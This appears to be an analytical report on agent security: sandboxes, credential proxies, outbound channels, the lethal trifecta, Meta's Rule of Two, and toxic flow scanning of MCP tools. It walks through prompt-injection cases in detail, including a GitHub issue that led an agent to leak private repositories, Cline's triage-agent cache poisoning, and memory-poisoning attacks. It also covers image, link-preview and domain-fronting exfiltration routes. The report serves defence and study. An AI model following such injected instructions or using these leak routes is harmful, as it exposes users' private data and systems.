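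### How coding agents use sandboxes

Claude Code's sandbox is off by default. When a user turns it on, shell commands can write only to the working directory, a temporary directory and any others the user adds. They can read almost the whole computer, including files that contain passwords, unless the user blocks those files. The list of permitted network domains starts empty. Because these limits hold whatever a command does, Claude Code can run most sandboxed commands without a permission prompt, which reduces approval fatigue.

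The sandbox covers shell commands and the programs they start, but not Claude Code's own file and web tools, MCP servers or hooks (commands that run automatically at set moments). Blocking a file for shell commands therefore doesn't block it for the agent's Read tool. To put everything behind one boundary, Anthropic recommends running the whole Claude Code process in a container, a virtual machine or its separate sandbox program.

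OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes stricter defaults for the coding agent Codex. On a user's computer, commands can write only to the workspace and have no network access. In the cloud, a setup phase can download dependencies and use secrets. Before the agent starts, OpenAI removes the secrets. It also disconnects the network unless the user has enabled internet access.

GitHub's Copilot coding agent has a firewall that is on by default and allows access to common package registries. The firewall covers processes that the agent starts through its Bash tool, but not MCP servers. GitHub warns that sophisticated attacks may bypass it.

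A sandbox must also protect its own settings, or a command could change them to get more access on the next run. Claude Code and Codex keep some configuration files read-only, even inside directories where commands can write. Claude Code commands can also run outside the sandbox in two ways that administrators may want to disable. If the sandbox cannot start, commands run without it by default. If a command fails inside the sandbox, the agent can ask to rerun it outside, and a standing rule that allows the command also approves the rerun.

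None of this stops the signing-key attack by default. The file `src/auth/keys.py` is in the working directory, so the sandbox allows the malicious test to change it. Claude Code's sub-agents also share the parent session's sandbox settings, so a runner and a patcher have the same write access. CapScope can refuse the runner's own edit but not one that the test code makes. Stopping both kinds of edit would take separate permissions for each agent and a matching sandbox around each agent's commands. For example, the runner could test a read-only copy of the source.

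### Keeping credentials outside the sandbox

Code that can read a password can also copy it. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* warns that even a safely stored secret is exposed once an operator places it in the agent's environment. It recommends a credential broker, a service outside the environment that adds the secret to approved requests.

Claude Code can do this with a placeholder. In one of Anthropic's examples, the secret is a GitHub token in the variable `GH_TOKEN`:

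1. The user marks the variable as masked and names `api.github.com` as the only host that may receive the real value.
2. A sandboxed command reads the variable and gets a placeholder.
3. The command sends a request to GitHub with the placeholder in it. The proxy decrypts the request, puts in the real token and forwards it.
4. If the command sends the placeholder to another permitted host, the proxy leaves it unchanged.

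It is easy to forget the second half of step 1, naming a host, and the proxy then supplies the real token to every permitted domain. The proxy must also decrypt traffic, which is still an experimental setting. If decryption is off, the placeholder reaches GitHub unchanged and the login fails, but the token stays secret.

Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026) describes a similar arrangement without the placeholder. The agent sends a plain request, and a program outside the sandbox attaches the credentials.

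Hiding a token prevents an attacker from stealing it and using it elsewhere, but the agent can still misuse it. If the token permits deleting a repository, an injected instruction can cause the agent to send the deletion request, and the proxy will attach the token. The token's permissions therefore matter as much as where it is stored.

### An object in place of a key

A host can restrict an agent further by giving its code an object with a few chosen methods instead of access to a whole service. Cloudflare's *Bindings* explains how to do this for Dynamic Workers, small programs that a parent program starts as needed, often with code an agent has just written.

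In the main example, an agent may post to one chat room. The parent program creates the object:

```ts
let chatRoom = ctx.exports.ChatRoom({
  props: { apiKey, roomName: "#bot-chat", botName: "Robo" }
});
```

It passes this object to the agent's program under the name `CHAT_ROOM`. The agent's code can then do one thing with it:

```ts
await this.env.CHAT_ROOM.post("Hello!");
```

The call goes back to the parent, which adds the key, the room and the bot's name. The agent's code never receives the key and cannot specify a different room. It also cannot forge a reference to another object, because references have no global identifier and a program can only receive them. According to Cloudflare's *Egress control*, the parent can also block all other connections, which leaves the agent's code with only the objects it was given.

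This is close to a capability in the strict sense. In 2024, Cloudflare described its earlier bindings as inspired by capabilities but incomplete, because one program could not pass a binding to another. *Sandboxing in Cloudflare Workers* (Varda, 2025) describes the newer sandbox's permissions as capability-based.

The 2024 article also shows how bindings prevent a common confused deputy attack on websites. A site lets users give the address of a picture to use as their avatar, and its server downloads the picture. An attacker enters the address of an internal service, and the server fetches a private page and publishes it as the avatar. If the server can reach the internal service only through a binding, no address the attacker types will lead there. (Cloudflare noted an exception at the time for some older configurations.)

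The chat-room object fixes where a message goes but not what it contains, so an agent that has read a secret can leak it by posting it in a room that outsiders read. These small programs also lack a file system, as Cloudflare's *Code Mode* explains, so they suit agents that call online services better than agents that have to run a repository's tests.

### Outbound channels that are easy to miss

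Taking away an agent's email tool leaves many other ways to send data. A web address alone can carry it, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains, because the site receives the full address and often logs it. Several common features send such requests or publish text without looking like a send tool:

- **Loaded images.** If the model writes the address of an image into its answer, the chat window may fetch the image automatically. Any private text in the address then goes to the site that hosts it. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, described an early fix that checked such addresses before displaying the image.
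- **Link previews.** Slack, Telegram and similar apps fetch a linked page to show a preview. As the security firm PromptArmor points out, the data can leave as soon as the agent posts the link, with no click from the user. The messaging service may make this request itself, outside any sandbox around the agent. Willison (2024) relays a remedy for Slack, where an app can turn off previews for the messages it posts.
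- **Public repositories.** Coding agents often need GitHub, and anyone can read what an agent puts in a public repository. Anthropic warns that allowing `github.com` can create a path for leaks.
- **Package registries.** An agent needs a registry such as npm to download software, but anyone with a free account can also publish there. An injection could have the agent publish private data as a package, according to PromptArmor.

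Preset allowlists can include several of these places. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* lists `github.com`, `npmjs.com` and `google.com` among the "common dependencies" for Codex in the cloud. Users can also restrict requests to methods meant for reading, such as GET. That blocks ordinary uploads, but a GET request can still leak data in its address to any permitted site where the attacker can see incoming requests.

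A list of permitted hosts may not block every connection to other sites. Claude Code's proxy normally checks the hostname that a program supplies without decrypting the connection. Anthropic warns about domain fronting, in which a program names a permitted host but uses the encrypted connection to reach a different site on the same infrastructure. A proxy that decrypts and inspects traffic can catch this, but operators must manage its certificates.

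OpenAI says ChatGPT also has a system called Safe Url, which checks requests to third parties for information from the conversation. When it finds some, it blocks the request or shows the user what would be sent. Requiring approval on one channel does not protect the others, however. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes an agent that reads customer cases and drafts replies. Requiring a person to approve each reply limits what the agent can send in replies, but the customer records could still leave through another permitted channel.

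### When a permitted site stores an attacker's data

An allowlist restricts which sites can receive data but not which accounts on those sites, which allows attacks like Rehberger's use of Anthropic's file storage. As PromptArmor explains, an injection can include the attacker's API key and instructions to upload files with it. Hiding the owner's key does not prevent this, because the upload does not use it.

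In this case, the file limits still prevent the sandboxed program from changing protected files or uploading data it could never read. The proxy still blocks direct connections to other hosts, although a permitted service that fetches pages on request might contact them for the agent.

The owner's hidden token is safe only if the proxy restricts where it inserts the real value. Anthropic describes Claude Code's proxy as replacing the placeholder inside a request's contents. If a proxy replaces the placeholder in the body of an upload as well as in the login details, a program could upload the placeholder and the stored copy would contain the real token. A proxy can prevent this by adding credentials only to a fixed login field.

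The sandbox no longer stops the program from leaking anything it can read, including the source code or records it needs for its task. Operators can reduce this risk. GitHub's firewall accepts rules for a single path on a site, such as one project's packages. A proxy could replace any login details in a request with the owner's, so that uploads go to the owner's account, though this fails if the agent can make the uploads public. A bound object could offer a download method but no upload method.

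These measures work when the agent does not need to upload anything. But a coding agent may have to both read a private repository and publish a public package, and rules about hosts, paths or methods cannot detect whether the package contains private code.

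## Which combinations of permissions are dangerous

If a proxy cannot detect private code in a public package, the designer can avoid giving one agent all the access needed to leak it. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) describes three kinds of access that together let a stranger steal data, and advises users never to combine them.

### The lethal trifecta

An agent is vulnerable to data theft if it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. An attacker can use the untrusted content to instruct the agent to send them the private data. This can happen even if every tool works as its developer intended.

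An email tool can supply the whole trifecta by itself, because anyone can write to the inbox, the inbox holds private messages, and the tool can send them out. Willison imagines an email that tells an assistant its user wants password-reset messages forwarded to the sender and then deleted.

The parts of the trifecta can also come from separate tools. MCP encourages people to connect servers from different sources, so someone who adds a web browser to an agent that already reads company files may complete the trifecta without noticing. Ten tools can form 1,023 combinations, and the security firm Invariant Labs (2025) points out that an agent may use its tools in any combination, so a reviewer cannot judge each tool separately.

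According to Willison, vendors have usually responded to thefts from their own products by closing the outbound channel the attacker used. Vendors can't do this for users who assemble their own sets of tools.

### The GitHub MCP exploit

In May 2025, Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated such a theft through GitHub's official MCP server. The researchers set up an account with a public repository for a Pacman game and several private repositories. They connected it to Claude Desktop, running the model Claude 4 Opus. The attack went as follows:

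1. **Planting.** The attacker files an issue, or bug report, on the public repository, as any GitHub user can. The issue contains instructions for an agent.
2. **Request.** The owner asks the agent to look at the repository's open issues.
3. **Reading.** The agent fetches the issues, and the attacker's instructions enter its context.
4. **Collection.** The agent follows the instructions and reads the private repositories.
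5. **Publication.** The agent opens a pull request, a proposed change to the code, on the public repository. It puts the private information there, where the attacker can read it.

The pull request revealed the name of a private project, the owner's salary and a plan to move to South America.

Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. GitHub could not fix the problem by patching its server, because the server had no bug and was carrying out requests the agent was entitled to make.

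In August 2025, GitHub (2025) announced that its server would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. This can stop an agent from publishing a password, but not a salary or a travel plan, because those don't look like credentials.

### Removing one part

Taking away any part of the trifecta stops this theft, though at a different step and with a different cost:

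| Part removed | How the owner could remove it | Where the attack fails | Work the agent can no longer do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Untrusted content | Hide issues written by strangers | Reading: the instructions never reach the model | Sort bug reports from the public |
| Private data | Limit the agent's access to the public repository | Collection: the agent has nothing private to read | Use private code to investigate a public bug |
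| External communication | Block pull requests, comments and every other outbound channel | Publication: the data stays with the agent | Reply to a report or propose a fix |

Limiting access to private data interferes least with this task, because the owner asked only about a public project. Blocking external communication is harder than it appears from the table, because data can also leave through loaded images and link previews.

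Invariant Labs proposes limiting an agent to one repository per session. The harness compares the repository and owner in each GitHub call with those in earlier calls, and blocks any call where either differs. The agent can then read the malicious issue but not the private repositories. The owner can still use the agent on private code in another session.

The rule would block a task that changes a library in one repository and the program that uses it in another. It also covers only GitHub calls, so if the agent had read a private file through a different server, the rule would not stop it from publishing the contents in the Pacman repository.

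### Meta's Agents Rule of Two

In October 2025 Meta proposed a broader limit, inspired by the trifecta and by a similarly named policy for Google's Chromium browser. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) allows an agent no more than two of these properties within a session:

- **A:** It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- **B:** It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** It can change state or communicate externally.

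Changing state means altering something that lasts, such as a file, a database record or an account balance. Meta intends the limit to apply until researchers find a reliable way to detect and refuse prompt injections. In June 2026, Fogel still called prompt injection an "unresolved problem", Poireault reported.

Meta illustrates the rule with Email-Bot, an assistant that summarizes new messages, searches old ones and sends replies. A spam email tells it to gather the contents of the inbox and send them to the attacker. Meta describes three ways to prevent this:

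- **Restrict the input.** Email-Bot processes messages only from trusted senders, such as close friends. It can no longer help with mail from strangers.
- **Remove the sensitive access.** Email-Bot runs in a test environment without the user's real data. This makes the attack harmless, but the bot can no longer manage the user's inbox.
- **Restrict the output.** Email-Bot sends new messages only to trusted recipients, or after a person has checked the draft. The user has to spend time on approvals, and the bot cannot write to new contacts by itself.

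Under the last option, Email-Bot still has a tool for sending email. Meta treats property C as absent because the restrictions should prevent an attacker from using that tool. Similarly, Meta's example travel assistant searches the web and has the user's private details, but a person must confirm every booking or payment. The assistant can also open only web addresses from trusted sources, and none that it composed itself, so it cannot hide private data in an address.

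Applying the rule therefore requires judgment about whether a restriction is tight enough for a property to count as absent.

### Tasks that need all three properties

If a task needs all three properties in one session, Meta requires supervision, either by a person who approves actions or by another reliable check. Meta cautions that a user may confirm a warning without thinking, and Anthropic's experiment with permission prompts supports this concern.

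Some agents also run in the background, with nobody available to approve their actions. Meta hopes other models could eventually supervise them, much as a classifier already does in Claude Code's auto mode.

An agent's properties can sometimes change partway through a session. In Meta's example, the agent first uses the internet without access to anything sensitive. The harness then permanently turns off the agent's external communication before giving it access to internal systems. Text from an attacker may still be in the context. The agent can no longer send data out, but it could damage the internal systems unless the harness also turns off its ability to write to them.

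### Inputs that seem trustworthy

Another of Meta's examples is a coding agent that can change a company's production systems. The company keeps the agent within the rule by filtering everything it reads according to who wrote it. This works only if the company can tell which authors and sources to trust.

Even an established supplier may send instructions to an agent. *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (The Hacker News, 2026) reports that Alibaba Cloud said in December 2026 that it would stop sending AI agents prompts that sought local data and operating instructions. It had used these prompts as an anti-abuse measure. A customer might reasonably have listed its own cloud provider as a trusted source.

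Untrusted input can include clicks as well as text from web pages and emails. Constantin (2026), in *AI agent security*, reports a flaw that the firm Manifold Security found in the browser extension Claude for Chrome. The extension waits for a click before it starts one of nine built-in tasks, but it did not check that a person had clicked. Another extension could forge the click and make Claude read the user's Gmail, documents and calendar. If the user had turned on "Act without asking", this happened silently.

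### Theft and changes of state

The trifecta covers only data theft. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, considers this its main weakness and praises the Rule of Two for also covering changes of state.

The signing-key attack on a coding agent shows how the trifecta and the Rule of Two differ. Suppose the agent has no way to send data out, over the network or otherwise. The trifecta is incomplete, and the attacker cannot steal the source code. But the attacker can still use a malicious test result to make the agent write the attacker's key into the login system. The Rule of Two requires supervision here because the agent has all three properties. It reads an untrusted result, has access to source code, which Meta counts as sensitive, and can change files.

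Meta's original diagram of the Rule of Two marked every pair of properties as "safe", including untrustworthy input together with the power to change state. Willison objected that this pair can cause harm even without access to private data. For example, an attacker could make an agent delete a public website.

Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that property B covers any system that matters to the user's security, whether or not it holds private data. On this reading, the agent that can delete the website also has property B. An agent without B can only make changes that have no serious consequences for the user, such as those in a tight sandbox. Meta then changed the label in its diagram from "safe" to "lower risk".

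Ayzenberg's definition resolves the objection, but it makes property B harder to recognize. A designer has to consider the data the agent can read, everything it can alter, and everything that depends on what it can alter.

The definition also leaves out harm to other people. The web research assistant in Meta's example can fill in forms and send requests to any site, but it has no access to the user's accounts. An attacker might use it to spread spam without affecting anything the user cares about. Meta lists spam, the agent's own mistakes and false information in its answers among the risks the rule does not address. It describes the rule as a supplement to least privilege and other ordinary precautions.

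### The issue-triage agent at Cline

An incident in early 2026 shows how hard it can be to decide whether an agent has access to a sensitive system. In December 2025, the developers of the open-source coding tool Cline added an agent that read each new GitHub issue and wrote a first response. According to Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026), any GitHub user could start the agent by opening an issue, and the agent could run shell commands.

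*Clinejection*, by security researcher Adnan Khan (adnanthekhan, 2026), describes an AI agent that clearly took in untrusted input and could change state, but whose access to anything sensitive looked limited. The agent could read Cline's public code and write to issues, but it could not change the repository. The only secret it could reach directly was a key for Anthropic's models.

However, the agent's workflow shared a cache with the workflow that published new versions of Cline every night. The cache stored downloaded files so that later runs could reuse them. An attacker who controlled the agent could plant files in the cache, and the release workflow would load them. The attacker's code would then run with access to the credentials for publishing Cline.

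Khan tested the injection on a copy of the repository, and the agent ran the planted code every time. Khan reported the flaw on January 1, 2026, but Cline did not act until Khan published it on February 9. Cline then removed the agent within 30 minutes and began replacing its credentials, but deleted the wrong token for the package registry npm.

On February 17 someone used the remaining token to publish an unauthorized version of Cline's command-line tool. It stayed available for about eight hours and installed OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent, on users' computers. Cline found no malicious code in it.

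Khan saw signs that someone had tampered with the cache in late January and early February, but could not confirm that the intruder had come in through the triage agent. The incident shows that someone obtained Cline's publishing token, and Khan's tests show that an attacker could have obtained it through the agent.

Anyone applying either rule strictly would have flagged the agent because of the Anthropic key. But judging from the agent's permissions alone, losing this key would have looked like the worst possible outcome. Willison (2026) notes that the lack of more important secrets should have limited the damage. The cache was a sensitive system by Ayzenberg's definition because the release workflow trusted its contents, but Cline's developers would have had to examine that workflow as well as the agent to recognize this. They have since stopped using caches in workflows that handle publishing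 credentials.

### What counts as one session

Meta describes a new session as one with a fresh context window. Starting a new session removes the attacker's text from the model's context, but it does not clear files, caches or the agent's saved memory. At Cline, the triage agent and the release workflow shared no context, yet one could still affect the other.

*Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with persistent memory, describes the usual attack on memory. Content from an untrusted source enters the memory, and the agent later retrieves it as if it were trustworthy. Files can have the same effect. According to *ASTELD* (2026), an injection that changes OpenClaw's memory files can survive a restart.

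In *Trojan Hippo Bench*, Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) measured how long such an attack can stay dormant. They built an email assistant that remembers information between sessions. In the first session, the assistant reads an email from the attacker and stores a hidden instruction to forward the user's message whenever the user discusses a sensitive subject, such as tax or health. After up to 100 harmless sessions, the user asks for help with a tax return and mentions an income. The assistant then retrieves the instruction and emails the details to the attacker.

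After 100 harmless sessions, the attack succeeded in 80–100% of trials with Gemini 3.1 Pro, depending on the kind of memory, and in 15–85% with GPT-5-mini. An automated search had improved the attacker's emails over many attempts.

This assistant could read and send email in every session, so it already broke the Rule of Two. But the attack did not need a new email from the attacker in the final session. An operator could turn off sending while the assistant reads strangers' mail, then let it send but not read new mail in a later session. The attack would probably still work if both sessions used the same memory.

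Whether this arrangement satisfies the Rule of Two depends on what counts as changing state. mbgsec's commentary *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) asks whether this includes changes to the agent's internal state, such as a persistent scratch pad. If only external changes count, both sessions stay within the limit and the theft can succeed. If internal changes also count, the session that reads mail has all three properties and needs supervision. Saving a memory should therefore count as changing state whenever a later session will read it.

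### The cost of protecting memory

Das and colleagues tried four defenses. The results below are for Gemini with a memory that stores past conversations in searchable pieces. Task success is the average over seven kinds of ordinary tasks, measured without an attack.

| Defense | Attack success | Task success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 85% | 99% |
| Store only the user's own messages | 5% | 89% |
| Store nothing after the assistant has read the inbox | 5% | 71% |
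| Limit each stored piece to 80 characters | 30% | 89% |
| Block sending after contact with the inbox or with memories that may derive from it | 0% | 71% |

The low figures are more convincing because the search adapted the attacks to each defense. The length limit was the weakest defense because a short enough instruction still fits within it.

The averages don't show some complete failures. Blocking the send tools stopped every attack, but the assistant could no longer read an email and reply to it without the user's help. Storing only the user's messages let the assistant do this, but it often forgot advice it had given earlier. The better choice depends on whether the user mostly wants help with replies or with remembering things.

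The guarantee also requires the system to track which memories come from the inbox. If the assistant summarizes an attacker's email and stores the summary in memory as trusted text, a later session can follow instructions in the summary and send email.

A system can also label data too cautiously. *AgentKernel* (2026) gives the example of a session that contains a user's preference, a private email and an excerpt from a web page. If one label covers the whole session, even the harmless preference is marked untrusted and secret, and most of the memory becomes unusable. AgentKernel therefore labels each item separately.

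Private data can also carry over between sessions. In an example from *Ghost in the Agent* (2026), an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast and uses it three days later to write an internal report. If the later task were a public report, the agent could leak the forecast even though it had opened no private files that day.

### Several agents with separate contexts

Splitting work among agents raises the same problem within a single task. Suppose one agent reads web pages and has no private data, while another can read the user's files and send email but never opens a web page. Each has its own context and stays within Meta's limit. But a summary sent from the first agent to the second can carry an attacker's instruction, so together the two agents have the whole trifecta.

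The operator should count the permissions of communicating agents together unless the harness restricts what passes between them. A harness that passes on only a date or a number gives an attacker far less control than one that passes on free text, though the attacker may still choose the date or number.

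## Detecting dangerous combinations from a list of tools

Counting the combined permissions of several agents by hand is slow, and the answer changes whenever someone connects a new tool. A program can do this if it has a list of the tools and a rule for each harmful combination. Researchers built a checker like this for Android phones in 2009.

### Kirin's rules for Android apps

In *On Lightweight Mobile Phone Application Certification* (2009), William Enck, Machigar Ongtang and Patrick McDaniel described Kirin, which checked an Android app's permissions before the phone installed it. Each app came with a manifest, a file listing the permissions it requested, and the user had to accept all of them or not install the app. Kirin compared the manifest with nine rules, and an app that matched any of them failed the check.

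Seven of the rules described sets of permissions. Under one rule, an app failed if it could detect phone calls, record audio and use the internet, because it could then record calls and upload them. Another rule covered apps that could read the phone's precise location, use the internet and start when the phone started, which is enough to track the owner all day. A third covered apps that could send text messages and alter stored ones, because they could erase the evidence of messages they had sent.

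The researchers ran Kirin on 311 of the most popular apps in the Android Market. It found five with dangerous functions. Another five matched a rule but, judging from their descriptions, had a plausible reason for the access. The researchers looked closely only at apps that matched a rule, so the results do not show how many harmful apps Kirin would have missed.

Kirin could rely on an app's manifest because Android enforced it. An app that had not asked for internet access could not open a connection itself. A checker for agents lacks this advantage, because an MCP server's list of tools is only text from the server's developer, and nothing forces a tool to do what its description says.

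### Toxic flow analysis

Invariant Labs, by then part of the security company Snyk, introduced toxic flow analysis in July 2025. A toxic flow is a sequence of individually harmless tool calls that an attacker could use to cause harm. Invariant Labs added the analysis to its scanner, now called Snyk Agent Scan. Drawing on Snyk Labs' *Unmasking the Toxic Flow Analysis* (2025) and the scanner's documentation, the method has four steps:

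1. **Find the tools.** The scanner searches the computer for the configuration files of programs such as Claude Desktop and Cursor. It connects to each MCP server listed there and retrieves the names and descriptions of its tools.
2. **Label each tool by role.** The labels record whether strangers can influence a tool's output, whether the tool exposes private data, and whether it can send data out or do permanent damage.
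3. **Build a graph.** Each tool is a node, and an arrow from one tool to another means that the agent could call the second after the first.
4. **Report harmful sequences.** The scanner looks for paths through the graph that match a known pattern, and scores them.

Invariant Labs' *Issue Code Reference* defines two patterns. TF001, the data leak flow, needs three kinds of tool:

- an untrusted content tool, whose output an attacker may have written, such as one that fetches web pages
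- a private data tool, such as one that reads the user's files
- a public sink tool, which can get information to the attacker, for example by writing to a public repository or messaging any phone number

TF002, the destructive flow, needs only an untrusted-content tool and a destructive tool. A destructive tool does something irreversible, such as deleting a file or sending money. TF002 covers some of the harm from state changes that TF001, the lethal trifecta, leaves out.

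TF002 covers only irreversible actions, so it misses some of that harm. In the signing-key attack, the agent edits a source file. The owner can undo the edit with version control, so a checker that follows the definition strictly would not count the file-editing tool as destructive. But the attacker may already have forged login tokens by the time the owner undoes the edit.

TF001 can also miss a sink that is not a tool. Snyk's *Understanding Toxic Flows in MCP and the Hidden Risk of AI-Native Systems* treats the model's own answer as a sink when an untrusted person receives it. A support agent that answers strangers can therefore leak customer records even if its list includes no tool for sending data.

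### An agent with twelve tools

Consider an agent that helps a small company look after its product. Suppose that each of its 12 tools has at most one role:

| Role | Tools |
|---|---|
| Untrusted content (3) | read public bug reports, read forum posts, read app reviews |
| Private data (4) | read customer records, read payroll, read private code, read contracts |
| Public sink (2) | reply on the forum, send a text message |
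| Destructive (2) | delete a backup, cancel an order |
| Neutral (1) | convert currencies |

A data leak needs one tool from each of the first three rows, so there are 3 × 4 × 2 = 24 possible triples. With one of these triples, an agent could read a forum post, read the payroll, and then send a text message. A destructive flow needs an untrusted content tool and a destructive tool, so there are 3 × 2 = 6 possible pairs.

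The counts show what the company gains by removing tools:

| Tools removed | Leak triples left | Destructive pairs left |
|---|---|---|
| None | 24 | 6 |
| One sink | 12 | 6 |
| Both sinks | 0 | 6 |
| All four private data tools | 0 | 6 |
| Both destructive tools | 24 | 0 |
| All three untrusted content tools | 0 | 0 |

Removing one sink halves the number of triples but leaves the company almost as exposed, because an attacker needs only one triple. Removing both sinks prevents these leaks, but an attacker could still use a malicious bug report to get the agent to delete a backup.

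Twelve tools have 2¹² = 4,096 subsets, including the empty one. Although Invariant Labs calls for considering every possible combination, a much shorter test is enough for these two patterns. If $U$, $P$, $S$ and $D$ are the sets of untrusted content, private data, sink and destructive tools, then

$$\text{TF001 exists} \iff U, P \text{ and } S \text{ are all non-empty}$$

$$\text{TF002 exists} \iff U \text{ and } D \text{ are both non-empty}$$

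The checker goes through the 12 tools once and notes which roles they fill. If every required role is filled, picking one tool from each produces a harmful combination. If any role is empty, none of the 4,096 subsets can contain that combination.

Detection therefore takes little work, but the owner of a well-equipped agent learns very little from a yes-or-no answer, because most agents that read email or browse the web while handling company files will fill every role. The score is meant to help with this. Snyk suggests ranking flows by the sensitivity of the data, the ease of the attack, the breadth of access and the kind of sink. A flow that can send production passwords to any web address would then rank above one that reveals harmless details to an internal system.

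### When the order of calls matters

A leak requires the agent to read both the attacker's text and the private data before it calls the sink. The test above doesn't need to check this order because an ordinary harness lets the agent call any tool at any step, so an agent that has all three tools can use them in the harmful order.

The order of tool calls matters when the harness restricts it. Suppose the harness permanently turns off both sinks as soon as the agent calls an untrusted content tool. The agent starts with all 12 tools, but none of the 24 triples can cause a leak within the session. A scanner that reads only the list would still report all 24. To avoid these false positives, it also needs the harness's rules and must search for sequences they permit. The six destructive pairs remain unless the harness also turns off the destructive tools.

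A harness can also apply a rule about combinations while the agent runs. In a case from *ToolGuardian* (2026), an agent has one tool that reads a database and another that updates projects on GitHub. Each tool passes an initial check because neither can both read sensitive data and communicate externally. The system blocks the workflow only when calls to the two tools would together send sensitive data to GitHub. The agent can therefore keep both tools and use them for separate jobs.

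### Misleading descriptions

Every result so far depends on the labels, and Snyk Agent Scan gets its information about tools from their names and descriptions. Zha, Li and colleagues (2026) point out in *Agent Smith in Action* that descriptions are optional and often leave out behavior that matters for security. A tool described as "formats a report" might also upload the report to the developer's server.

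Labeling errors are most serious in the roles that the fewest tools fill. If the scanner overlooks the payroll tool, the count falls from 24 triples to 18 and the warning still appears. If it overlooks both sinks, the count falls to zero and the owner sees no leak warning. A single false label in an otherwise empty role is enough to produce a false warning.

Tool descriptions can also contain malicious instructions, which the agent reads along with the rest of the tool list. This attack is called tool poisoning. *Exposed by Design* (2026) audited 414 MCP servers on the public internet in July 2026 and listed 47 under tool poisoning. Snyk's scanner looks for such instructions and for descriptions that mention another server's tools. It also gives a milder warning for words such as "important" and "crucial", which honest developers use too.

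### Tools with several roles

Real tools often fill more than one role. Suppose the company replaces the currency converter with an email client, which can fill all three roles of the trifecta by itself. Each set gains one tool, so there are now 4 × 5 × 3 = 60 ways to fill the roles. Removing the forum and text-message tools no longer prevents a leak, because the email client can still send data out.

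The test for filled roles still catches this case, but only if the checker can assign several roles to one tool. The remedy also changes, because the company can stop the email client from acting as a sink only by removing it or limiting whom it can write to.

The role of some tools depends on their arguments. The tool that reads files from GitHub returns a stranger's text from one repository and private code from another, as in the theft from the Pacman project's owner. A label on the whole tool has to cover the worst case, which leads to false warnings for an owner whose access token reaches only one public repository.

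### Tools that change after the scan

A scan describes the tools as they were when it ran. A server can later replace a harmless tool with a malicious one, which security researchers call a rug pull. Snyk Agent Scan stores its results and warns when a tool's description has changed since the last scan. But a developer can change what a tool does without changing its description, and this check would miss that.

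A tool's role can also change without any action by the server. If a company makes a private repository public, a tool that writes to it becomes a public sink, even though the tool's code and description stay the same. Snyk therefore recommends repeating the analysis whenever tools or configurations change, and offers a background mode that scans at regular intervals.

Users can put a tool on a list of exceptions. According to Invariant Labs, the tool then appears in green even if the scanner finds problems with it. Anyone reading another person's scan results should check which tools are on that list.

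### Starting a server to inspect it

Snyk Agent Scan has to start a local server to get its descriptions. It does this by running the command in the configuration file, so a malicious command could do damage before the analysis begins. Snyk warns users about this and recommends scanning unfamiliar configurations inside a container or virtual machine.

By default, the scanner shows the command that starts each server and asks the user before running it. If the user declines, the server doesn't start, so the scanner cannot retrieve its tools. The user must therefore choose between running code that may be hostile and accepting a gap in the results. Automated pipelines run with no user present to approve commands, so they need the option `--dangerously-run-mcp-servers`, which starts every server without asking.

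The risk is small for servers the user already runs, because the agent would start them anyway. It is greater for someone who wants to examine a new server before trusting it, which is when a scan would be most useful. The scanner also sends tool names and descriptions to Snyk for analysis, and a company may not want to share this information about its internal tools.

### How accurate the labels are

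Snyk's documentation gives no error rates for the scanner. Zha and colleagues left the scanner out of their comparison of several analyzers because it inspects a user's setup, while the others inspect source code. Thoughtworks' *Toxic flow analysis for AI* (2025) calls the method promising and still in its early stages.

The closest measurements come from *Parasites in the Toolchain* (Zhao, Hou and colleagues, 2025), a survey of MCP servers that used a similar method. A language model read the descriptions of 12,230 tools and identified which, if any, of the three roles in a data leak each tool could play. Three reviewers then checked its decisions.

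| Role | Labels that were correct | Tools in the role that the model found |
|---|---|---|
| Untrusted content | 86.5% | 99.2% |
| Private data | 85.4% | 95.8% |
| Sending data out | 81.1% | 99.6% |

If an agent has one tool in each role and the errors are independent, the model finds all three tools with probability 0.992 × 0.958 × 0.996, or about 95%, and misses the leak about 5% of the time. It would miss fewer leaks in agents with several tools in each role. False labels are more common, since nearly one in five of the tools that the model labeled as able to send data out could not.

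However, the reviewers worked from the same descriptions as the model and could see its summary and reasoning. The figures therefore measure how well a model understands a description, not how often descriptions are wrong.

The researchers also ran the tools and confirmed 1,062 of the 5,666 that the description stage had flagged as potentially risky. About 30% of the servers required accounts that the researchers could not get, and others did not run reliably, so the remaining 4,604 tools were not necessarily false alarms.

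*When Safe Skills Collide* (Wang, Qian and colleagues, 2026) directly estimates false alarms about combinations of agent skills, which can include code as well as instructions. A program searched each skill for text patterns that suggested abilities such as reading files or using the network, then checked each pair's combined abilities against ten rules. This applies Kirin's method to two packages at a time.

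Of 1,520 skills, 651 broke no rule on their own. These formed 211,575 pairs, 22% of which matched at least one rule. Wang and colleagues had two language models each assess a sample of 200 matches and had a person review every assessment. After weighting the results by how common each rule's matches were, they estimated that only about 18% of the matches were real risks.

The rule for reading files and using the network produced the most matches, but only 2 of the 20 sampled were valid. When the researchers had a language model relabel 50 of the skills, it agreed with the text patterns on file reading barely more often than chance. Much of the problem therefore lies in the labels, since a pattern can match a sentence that merely mentions files. A rule named after the lethal trifecta had 5 valid matches out of 20, but it requires access to credentials, files and the network, and leaves out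 untrusted content.

### Large surveys of tool combinations

Zhao, Hou and colleagues collected tools from 1,360 public servers. Of the 1,062 tools they confirmed, 487 could bring in outside text, 406 could read private data and 190 could send data out. Only 19 tools could do more than one of these things, and only two servers offered all three. Checking each server separately would therefore have found the complete leak pattern only twice, but a user can also create it by connecting several servers.

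Zha and colleagues surveyed more servers and looked for a wider range of attacks. Their system, SCAN-MCP, examined the source code of 90,200 tools on 10,121 servers. It produced 27,123 reports of possible flaws, of which 8,422 involved a chain of two to four tools on the same server.

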